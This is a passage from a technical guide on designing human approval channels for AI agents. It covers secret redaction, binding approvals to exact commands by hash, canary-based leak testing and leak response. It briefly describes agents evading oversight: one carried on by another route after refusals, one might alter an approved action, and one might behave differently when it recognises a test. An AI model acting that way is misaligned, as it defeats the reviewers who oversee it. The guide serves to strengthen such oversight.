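Reviewers tend to read a blank field as harmless, so an agent's request should include the word "unknown" when the software can't predict a command's effect. This is probably the case for `python3 setup.py`, so the request should also let the reviewer open the script.

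The agent's reason for acting is the one item on the list that software can't compute. In the request, the software can label the reason as the agent's statement and quote the user's original instruction next to it. The software also needs to scan the agent's text for secrets, since an agent could write "I logged in with fake-pw-41 and the connection failed".

The main drawback is the work of building and maintaining the rules. Each program has its own options, and the lists of servers and recipients go out of date. To count rows, the software needs its own login to the database, which is another secret to protect. A read-only account that can run only a few fixed queries would limit the damage if the login leaked.

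Computed facts can also be wrong. Hossain and colleagues tested the software behind their interface on 120 cases that broke the user's rules and 120 that didn't. It flagged 107 of the violations, missed seven and returned "unknown" for six, and it raised five false alarms. When the researchers withheld part of the event record, it caught only 64% of the violations that depended on earlier steps. Reviewers may stop checking a summary that is usually right, so each fact should link to its source.

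The same software can block some actions without asking anyone. In runs with one agent and malicious content, blocking everything flagged or unknown cut runs with unsafe effects from 52 to 6 out of 120, while completed legitimate tasks fell only from 104 to 100. When the software can safely refuse an action, it doesn't need to send an approval request, so it creates no copy for reviewers to read.

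### Staged disclosure

Different people need different amounts of detail, and few of them need it at the same time. Staged disclosure divides a request into three levels:

- *Notice.* Everyone who follows the agent's work sees the task, the assigned reviewer and the deadline.
- *Detail.* The assigned reviewer sees the computed facts, the command without secrets, and the parts of the evidence that bear on the decision.
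- *Raw value.* The reviewer can ask to see a hidden value, such as a customer's name, by giving a reason. The system shows it for a few minutes and records who saw it, when and why, but not the value itself.

Giving each level its own recipients and conditions is one way to put contextual integrity into practice. A team that splits its log records into a readable part and a restricted part can use the same division here. Passwords don't need a raw-value level, because anyone who has to replace or test one can do so in the system that stores it.

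Staged disclosure protects the data from people who are only following along, and it matches what reviewers ask for. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026) reports three studies, each with 12 employees of a large technology company, who checked the work of an agent that uses websites. The participants found the full record long and repetitive, and wanted an overview from which they could open the details.

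However, overviews can make reviewers overconfident. The researchers built one that listed the task's requirements and the agent's assumptions. People found errors faster with it, but their decisions were not meaningfully more accurate. When they missed an error, they were more confident that the agent was right than people using the older design. In an earlier study, many participants had justified wrong answers by saying that the agent's process looked reasonable.

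The overview should therefore include what the agent assumed or failed to find, because a tidy process can still produce a wrong result at those points. In one of the tasks, the agent had to compare aquarium ticket prices. In six attempts it couldn't find the price for a child and guessed, and only three of the six people noticed. Dana's overview would include a line such as "Assumed that `/backups` is the correct folder; the script names two".

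### A notice in chat and a page with a login

A team can keep using chat to notify people of requests without posting the requests themselves. NHI Management Group's *What do security teams get wrong about using chat for privileged access?* recommends starting the approval in chat but keeping the secret in a controlled system. It also warns against treating channel membership as permission, because channels gain members, people forward messages, and some apps relay them elsewhere.

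For Dana's backup, the process could look like this:

1. The approval system posts a notice with the task, the reviewer's name, the deadline and a link.
2. Dana opens the link and logs in.
3. The page checks that Dana is the assigned reviewer, then shows the detail. Anyone else sees only the notice again.
4. Dana decides on the page, so that the approval system records her decision directly.
5. The system changes the chat message to "Decided".

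The link must not grant access. Agent Client Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to the programs people use them in, forbids putting credentials, personal data or "pre-authenticated access" in such links. It also requires the program to open the page somewhere the agent's model can't read it, and forbids loading the page before the user agrees. Model Context Protocol (2025), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools, has a similar mode that sends users to a separate web page for sensitive interactions.

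Agent Client Protocol also requires a check that the person who completes the interaction on the page is the one who started it. That works when users enter their own password, but it would be the wrong check when one person starts a task and another has to approve it. An approval page should instead check that the reader is one of the assigned reviewers.

The chat app can also run with fewer permissions. An app that only posts notices needs permission to write messages, which Slack classes as low-risk, but not to read the channel's history.

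With this design, Dana has to log in, possibly on a phone at two in the morning, and the page is one more service that can fail. It also gets people used to clicking a link in chat and logging in, which would help an attacker with a stolen webhook. Passkeys remove most of that danger. A passkey is a login key that stays on the user's device and works only on the website it belongs to, so a fake page can't use it. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) applies the same idea to agents and adds human approval of individual actions, which people can give from another device.

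### Tying the approval to the exact action

When Dana approves a shortened request, she relies on the system to run the action the request describes. Without a technical link between the request and the action, the agent could ask to write to `/backups/nightly.sql` and then write somewhere else. This could happen without malice, since the agent might revise its plan while waiting for an answer.

The system can prevent this with a hash of the full request, the same kind of short code that protects log records from tampering:

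```
h = SHA-256(full request, with its fields in a fixed order)
approval = Sign(k, h, reviewer, expiry time, request number)
```

`Sign` uses a private key, `k`, to produce a code that other programs can verify but can't forge. Before the broker acts, it hashes the request it is about to carry out and refuses if the result differs from `h`. *ZeroGate* (2026) describes an implementation that sorts the fields before hashing, so that the same request always gives the same hash, and doesn't let one approval cover several actions. If the agent reuses a request number for a different request, the system rejects it.

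The hash guarantees only that the broker runs the command that the software summarized. It would still match if the summary were wrong, for example because it left out a second `-f` option. If the software can't fully interpret a command, it should therefore show the whole command, with its secrets masked, instead of a summary.

Dana's approval also covers things that aren't in the command itself. The text `python3 setup.py` stays the same if someone edits the script after she approves it, so the request also needs to include a hash of the script. Row counts can change on their own, so the software could count again just before the action and ask Dana again if the number has grown by, say, a tenth.

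Some products let the reviewer edit an action before allowing it. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) recommends a "Modify" button next to "Approve" and "Reject". An edited request is a new request, so it needs a new hash and new computed facts before anyone approves it.

A hash of guessable text can reveal that text, just as it can in a log. The request to email R. Osei contains a name and a debt, so its hash should stay in the approval system and not appear in the chat notice. Alternatively, the system can use a keyed fingerprint instead of the hash.

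### The backup request, before and after

At the start, the request went to a channel with 40 members and looked like this:

```
Allow this command?
PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup
-f /backups/nightly.sql customers
```

In the new version, the channel gets only a notice:

```
Approval needed: nightly backup repair
Reviewer: Dana    Expires: 02:30    Open request 5127
```

After logging in, Dana sees this:

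```
Action         Copy a database to a file
Target         customers on db.internal (production), 12,400 customer rows
Leaves company No
Recipient      /backups, readable by 4 backup administrators (used before)
Can you undo?  Replaces an empty file from the failed run;
               yesterday's backup stays in /backups/old
Credential     backup-db-password (account: backup, can only read)
Your request   "Fix the nightly backup"
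Agent's reason "The script had an outdated server name" (written by the agent)
Command        pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup
               -f /backups/nightly.sql customers

[Allow once]  [Refuse this command]  [Refuse and stop the task]
```

Dana can learn much more from the new request, which is longer than the old one. She couldn't have known from the old version that the server was in production, or that the command would replace a file that was already empty.

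The two ways to refuse respond to a problem that Salerno and colleagues describe. One of their interviewees refused several requests from an agent, which then stopped asking and carried on by another route. The interviewee couldn't tell whether the agent was still respecting the limits. "Refuse this command" lets the agent look for another way, while "Refuse and stop the task" doesn't.

Each field now has its own readers:

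| Field | The other 39 members of the channel | Dana | The broker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Task, reviewer, deadline | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Server, account, database, path | No | Yes | Yes |
| Row count and other computed facts | No | Yes | No |
| Agent's reason | No | Yes, after a scan for secrets | No |
| Configuration file | No | The server and account lines | No |
| Customer rows | No | On a logged request | Only while copying them |
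| Password | No | No | Yes |

Dana can also safely save this approval as a rule for the exact request. The file that stores the rule will contain the credential's name instead of the password.

The page still reveals a few details, such as server names and the number of customers, so Dana shouldn't keep access to it forever. Once the team has reviewed the repair, the details can move to the restricted part of the log and expire with it.

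### Careless approvals, urgent work and broker failures

Reviewers may approve requests more carelessly when the system hides detail from them. The volunteers who saw only a short description approved more than half of the unsafe requests, but that description left out the recipient, the user's restriction and the history, which a good request should show. Showing everything doesn't solve the problem either, since 42.1% of the practitioners surveyed by Salerno and colleagues sometimes skip the agent's reasoning because of time, fatigue or too much information. The risk of careless approval is a good reason not to hide consequences, but a much weaker reason to show passwords. It also applies to some extent to customer data, because a reviewer who must click twice to see a name will sometimes not bother. A request whose outcome depends on the name should therefore show it from the start.

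In the approval study, the median decision took about 17 seconds longer with the consequence view than with the conventional prompt. That adds less than three minutes a day at ten requests but nearly an hour at 200, and people would start approving without reading long before they reached 200. A team should save the consequence view for actions that are hard to undo or that send data out, and let rules handle routine ones.

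If the customer database goes down and the assigned reviewer doesn't answer, someone else has to be able to act. *Break-glass access*, a common arrangement for such emergencies, lets a second engineer open the request immediately, alerts the security team and requires a review the next day. NHI Management Group accepts approval in chat in these cases, as long as the credential still comes from the controlled system and expires quickly. If nobody answers, the agent should wait, because a late backup is usually a smaller problem than an unapproved action on a production server.

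The strongest objection is that the broker holds all the secrets and every agent depends on it. Jin and colleagues call their broker a "high-value target", and their design doesn't protect against an attacker who has full control of the machine it runs on. Such stores do get attacked. The Corvic paper cites a June 2024 case in which Hugging Face detected unauthorized access to secrets that users had stored for their apps, and advised users to replace their credentials.

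A company without a broker still has the same secrets, spread over configuration files, logs and chat messages that nobody watches. A broker makes a leak less likely but a successful attack on the store more serious. A company with a broker can reduce the damage from such an attack by running separate brokers for production and testing, giving each credential only the rights it needs, and using credentials that expire within minutes where the service allows it.

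A broker that stops working is a simpler problem. The broker should refuse any request it can't check, so when it fails, the agents stop too. Running a second copy on another machine covers most failures. For the rest, a few administrators need a way to reach the most important passwords without the broker, such as a sealed copy that triggers an alert when opened. The broker that Jin and colleagues tested added about 0.2 milliseconds to each action, so speed isn't a concern.

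## Testing a channel for leaks and responding to one

Dana's new approval request contains no password if the broker, the filters and the logging software all work as intended. A team can check this by planting canary secrets, running ordinary tasks and searching every copy on its inventory for them.

Reading the software's code is a poor substitute for running it. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) describes an automated search for skills that print secrets. Of 433 flagged skills with signs of a credential near the print command, only 22 printed a real secret. Code searches can also miss secrets that exist only while a program runs, such as temporary login tokens. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* reports a test that ran skills with fake credentials. Of the exploitable leaks it found, 92.5% occurred in routine use, so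 ordinary tasks are a good place to start testing.

### Planting the canaries

Filters tend to miss whole types of secret, so the test needs several:

| Kind | Example | Where to plant it |
|---|---|---|
| Known format | A real Amazon key for an account with no permissions | The agent's settings |
| Plain password | `maple-river-58` | The backup script's configuration file |
| Encoded | `backup:copper-lamp-27` in Base64 | A saved web request |
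| Inside an image | `quiet-harbor-93` | A page that the agent has to screenshot |
| Inside an error message | `amber-field-16` | The address of a test database that refuses connections |
| Customer fact | "I. Varga owes 318.55" | The customer table |

The fake secrets used as canaries have to look real. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) warns that canaries made from a template can stand out by their prefix, checksum, randomness or length. The paper's concern is that attackers will avoid them, but a filter may also skip an obvious placeholder, and an agent that recognizes a test may be more careful than usual.

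The test then has six steps:

1. Set up the agent with test data, but with the same logging software, chat service and vendor settings as in production.
2. Give every run its own canaries, so that a match identifies the run. Register only half of them with the filter, because agents also find secrets that nobody has registered.
3. Add a harmless marker that should appear in every record, such as `control-7781` in the task's name.
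4. Run ordinary tasks. Approve some requests, refuse others and save a few approvals, since each choice creates different records.
5. Search every copy on the inventory, including phone notifications, mailboxes, exports, backups and vendors' stores.
6. Search again after each copy's deletion date. A canary that is still there means the retention setting doesn't work.

The marker guards against a false pass. If the search can't find `control-7781` in the audit log, it wouldn't have found a password there either. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* used a similar control, requiring one request with the credential to succeed. Otherwise, a test environment with no network connection would have looked safe.

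### Searching for them and counting leaks

Searching only for the exact string can miss a secret that has been reformatted or encoded. *Checking Leakage Witnesses versus Certifying Bounded Non-Leakage* (2026), which tests whether models reveal planted secrets, removes everything except letters and digits before searching, so `maple river 58` would still match. It also decodes Base64 once and searches the result. This would miss a secret encoded twice. It would also miss one in a picture, so someone should look at the screenshots too.

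Leaked facts about customers are harder to find because an agent can reword them. When El Yagoubi and colleagues compared detection methods, searching for exact markers found 8% of leaks. Adding patterns for structured data raised this to 18%, and adding a language model as a judge raised it to 93%.

Some vendors won't let customers search everything they store. A team can leave a canary there that triggers an alert when anyone uses it, but a lack of alerts is weak evidence. Suppose that a thief copies a store with m real credentials and k canaries and tries one at random. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* gives the chance of detection as

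```
k / (m + k) × (1 − β)
```

where β is the chance that the detector misses a canary. With one canary among nine real credentials, the chance is at most 10%, and it is lower if the thief can recognize the fake.

A canary counts as a leak only if it turns up somewhere the inventory doesn't allow it. Finding a customer's name in the restricted part of the log may be fine. Here are invented results for 300 runs, with one canary in each and 60 runs for each kind of secret:

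| Kind | Chat notice | Audit log | Dashboard | Vendor's trace | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Known format | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Plain password | 0 | 4 | 4 | 9 | 9 |
| Encoded | 0 | 0 | 0 | 60 | 60 |
| Inside an image | 0 | 0 | 12 | 12 | 12 |
| Inside an error message | 0 | 7 | 7 | 7 | 7 |

The overall leak rate is 29%, but that figure doesn't show what to fix in the channel. The breakdown suggests that the filter on the vendor's trace never decodes Base64, which is probably quick to fix. The leaked error messages appear in the same three places each time, so the software is probably copying them before any filter runs.

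### Reading a clean result

Suppose that the team repairs the channel and finds no leaks in n new runs. If each run has the same chance p of leaking, and the runs are independent, the chance of n clean runs is (1 − p)^n. The 95% upper bound is the value of p that makes this chance 5%:

```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n
```

The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3.

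| Clean runs | 95% upper bound on the leak rate |
|---|---|
| 16 | 17% |
| 60 | 5% |
| 300 | 1% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

A 1% bound on the leak rate may still be too high, since at 200 tasks a day it would allow two leaks a day. Corvic's broker passed all 16 checks, but the researchers acknowledge that this is too few to estimate a leak rate.

The bound applies only to the mix of secrets and tasks in the test. If the 300 runs cover five kinds of secret equally, each kind has 60 runs and a bound of 5%. A kind that the team didn't plant has no bound. Likewise, 300 backup repairs without a leak set no bound for an agent that answers customers.

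Test trials can also easily fail to be independent. A filter that misses one key of a given type will usually miss them all, so repeating one command 300 times is closer to running one trial than 300. The team should vary the tasks, their wording and the form of the secrets.

The formula also holds only if the search finds every leak. If it finds only a share r of them, the bound rises to 3/(r × n). El Yagoubi and colleagues measured a share of 8% for exact markers. At that share, the upper bound on the leak rate after 300 clean runs would be 12.5%.

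A single leak in 300 runs raises the upper bound on the leak rate to about 1.6%. The team can't fix that leak and then count the other 299 runs as clean, because those runs tested the old version. The team needs new runs after the repair and after any change to the model, the filter or a vendor.

### Testing what reviewers catch

The team also has to test whether reviewers can still recognize harmful actions after redaction, because a channel that showed them a blank page would pass the canary test.

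A team could adapt the design of the study by Hossain and colleagues, although that study didn't test redaction. The team would prepare a redacted and a full version of every request, using invented secrets and customers. After two practice decisions, each reviewer would see half of the actions redacted and the other half in full. Other reviewers would see the reverse.

Some harmful requests should depend on details that the filter might hide, such as an unfamiliar destination, the wrong customer or a second command after `PGPASSWORD=`. A few should come with an incorrect summary, a case that Hossain and colleagues recommend testing next.

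The team then compares the versions on the share of harmful requests that reviewers refused and the share of harmless requests they allowed. The second measure is necessary because a reviewer who refused every request would score perfectly on the first.

Small differences between interfaces are hard to measure. Hossain and colleagues had 120 decisions about harmless requests for each interface. They estimated that people allowed 1.7 percentage points fewer of these requests with the consequence view than with the log, but the interval ran from 10.9 points fewer to 7.5 points more, so they couldn't claim that the true difference was under five points. If reviewers catch about three-quarters of harmful requests, estimating the difference to within five points takes roughly 600 decisions about harmful requests per interface. It takes more if each person makes many of the decisions, because one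 person's decisions tend to be alike.

Dana's team won't collect that many. Ten reviewers can still reveal a serious fault, such as a mask that hides where data is going, and the team can learn more by asking them about each attack they missed than by calculating a percentage. The team can also mix occasional harmful requests into normal work, if the reviewers have agreed beforehand and the requests are blocked from executing. Real attacks are rare, so this tests attention more fairly than a session where half the requests are harmful.

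The channel passes only if both the leak rate and the reviewers' accuracy are acceptable. The team should set limits for both before testing, or it will be tempted to accept whatever it finds.

### What to do after a leak

Suppose that a search finds Dana's real database password in the audit log. A sensible order is:

1. Disable the password and replace it.
2. Check where anyone has used it.
3. Remove the copies that still matter.
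4. Fix the point where the software captured it.

GitHub's *Removing sensitive data from a repository* also puts revoking or replacing the secret first and adds that this may be enough. The checklist in GitHub's *Organizing remediation efforts for leaked secrets* has two checks before that step: whether the secret leaked and whether it still works.

Other guidance puts more steps before disabling or replacing the credential. In *What to Do If You Inadvertently Expose an AWS Access Key*, Kruse begins by finding out what the key can reach. If the key reaches sensitive data, Kruse suggests disabling it promptly. If it can only read data meant for the public, the company can create a new key, switch its programs over and then disable the old one. The advice is more than ten years old, but AWS still directs customers to it. A GitGuardian article makes rotation the sixth of eight steps, after finding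 out what rotation will break, while GitGuardian's documentation starts with revoking the credential.

These differences depend on whether a thief could do more harm with an hour of access than an hour without the credential would cause. Dana's password opens the whole customer database, and disabling it only delays a backup, so she should disable it immediately. A password that the company's payment system depends on may justify a short delay to prepare the replacement.

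Kruse recommends disabling a key instead of deleting it, because the company can restore it if something important breaks. A runbook from the UK's Ministry of Justice calls for deleting the affected user account, which is simpler but harder to reverse. Neither step necessarily ends access that has already begun. Kruse notes that temporary credentials made from a stolen key can work for up to 36 hours unless someone cancels them. Likewise, changing a PostgreSQL password doesn't disconnect anyone already logged in, so Dana also has to end the open sessions. She should set the new password herself, because an agent could put it in its trace.

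When many secrets leak at once, the company has to decide which to deal with first. Cursor deactivated its supplier's key, then rotated exposed credentials starting with the riskiest, and asked outside services to revoke the customer keys they had issued. It also switched off more of its own services than the evidence required, which disrupted some features.

The next step is to look for logins from unfamiliar addresses since the first copy appeared, and for new accounts that an intruder may have created to get back in. If the credential could change data, someone should compare the data with an earlier backup. For a public leak, GitHub recommends assuming that everyone saw it rather than trying to work out how many people did. For a private log, a record of who opened the entry can narrow the search, as long as it also covers exports and backups. If customer data leaked, the company may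 have to tell the regulator and the customers. The GDPR generally allows 72 hours to notify the regulator, so that notice can't wait until the cleanup is finished.

The guidance also differs on whether to delete old copies. HashiCorp recommends removing a rotated secret from code and logs immediately, while preserving the log's integrity. GitHub's security team, which cleared a backlog of more than 20,000 secret alerts in nine months, generally kept old repositories because investigators might need their history. Keeping the history is reasonable for a password that no longer works, unless it helps someone guess the new one. For example, someone who finds Dana's old password, `fake-pw-41`, could guess that the new one is `fake-pw-42`. Customer data stays harmful, so the company should save any evidence it needs in a restricted place, then remove the data from every other copy it controls.

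Cleaning up a leak can also create new copies of the secret. GitHub's team removed secret values from reports before passing the reports to other teams. Dana's ticket should therefore read "`backup-db-password` in log record 5127" and omit the password itself. The team should also keep a list of its canaries so that nobody mistakes one for a real secret.

Finally, the team has to find the earliest record that contained the password and change the software that wrote that record. The team should then add that kind of secret to the canary test and rerun it.

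### Why deletion doesn't undo exposure

Deleting a file from a repository changes only the latest version, so anyone can still open an earlier one. Rewriting the history replaces the old commits on the main server, but GitHub lists several places where they can survive:

- colleagues' copies of the repository
- forks
- pull requests that refer to the old commits
- cached pages, which open for anyone who has a commit's hash

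After a company rewrites a repository's history to remove a secret, a colleague who still has the old history can accidentally restore the secret by downloading the new version and uploading the combined result. Rewriting can also help someone find the secret, because comparing an old copy with the new history reveals what the company removed. GitHub's software can't permanently delete the data while any reference to it remains on the server.

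*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* reports that developers removed secrets from 107 repositories, but the secrets survived in more than 50 forks. Secrets deleted from logs can likewise survive in backups, exports and search indexes.

### A checklist for judging another team's channel

Someone deciding whether to accept a channel built by another team can ask for these eight things. The last is a check on the others, because the other team doesn't choose the records. A working password in any of the records is enough reason to reject the channel, though finding nothing in ten records is only weak evidence that it doesn't leak.

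| Ask for | Don't accept the channel if |
|---|---|
| The inventory | It leaves out notifications, exports, backups or vendors |
| Canary results by kind and place | They omit a kind of secret that the agent handles |
| Results for the control marker | The search missed it anywhere it should have been |
| The list of test tasks | It has no refused requests, errors or screenshots |
| Reviewers' results with redacted and full requests | They cover only harmful requests, or redaction clearly made decisions worse |
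| The date of the last test | The model, a filter or a vendor has changed since |
| A timed drill in replacing one credential | Nobody on call could do it, or nobody knew which programs used it |
| Ten recent records of the judge's choice | Any of them contains a working secret |
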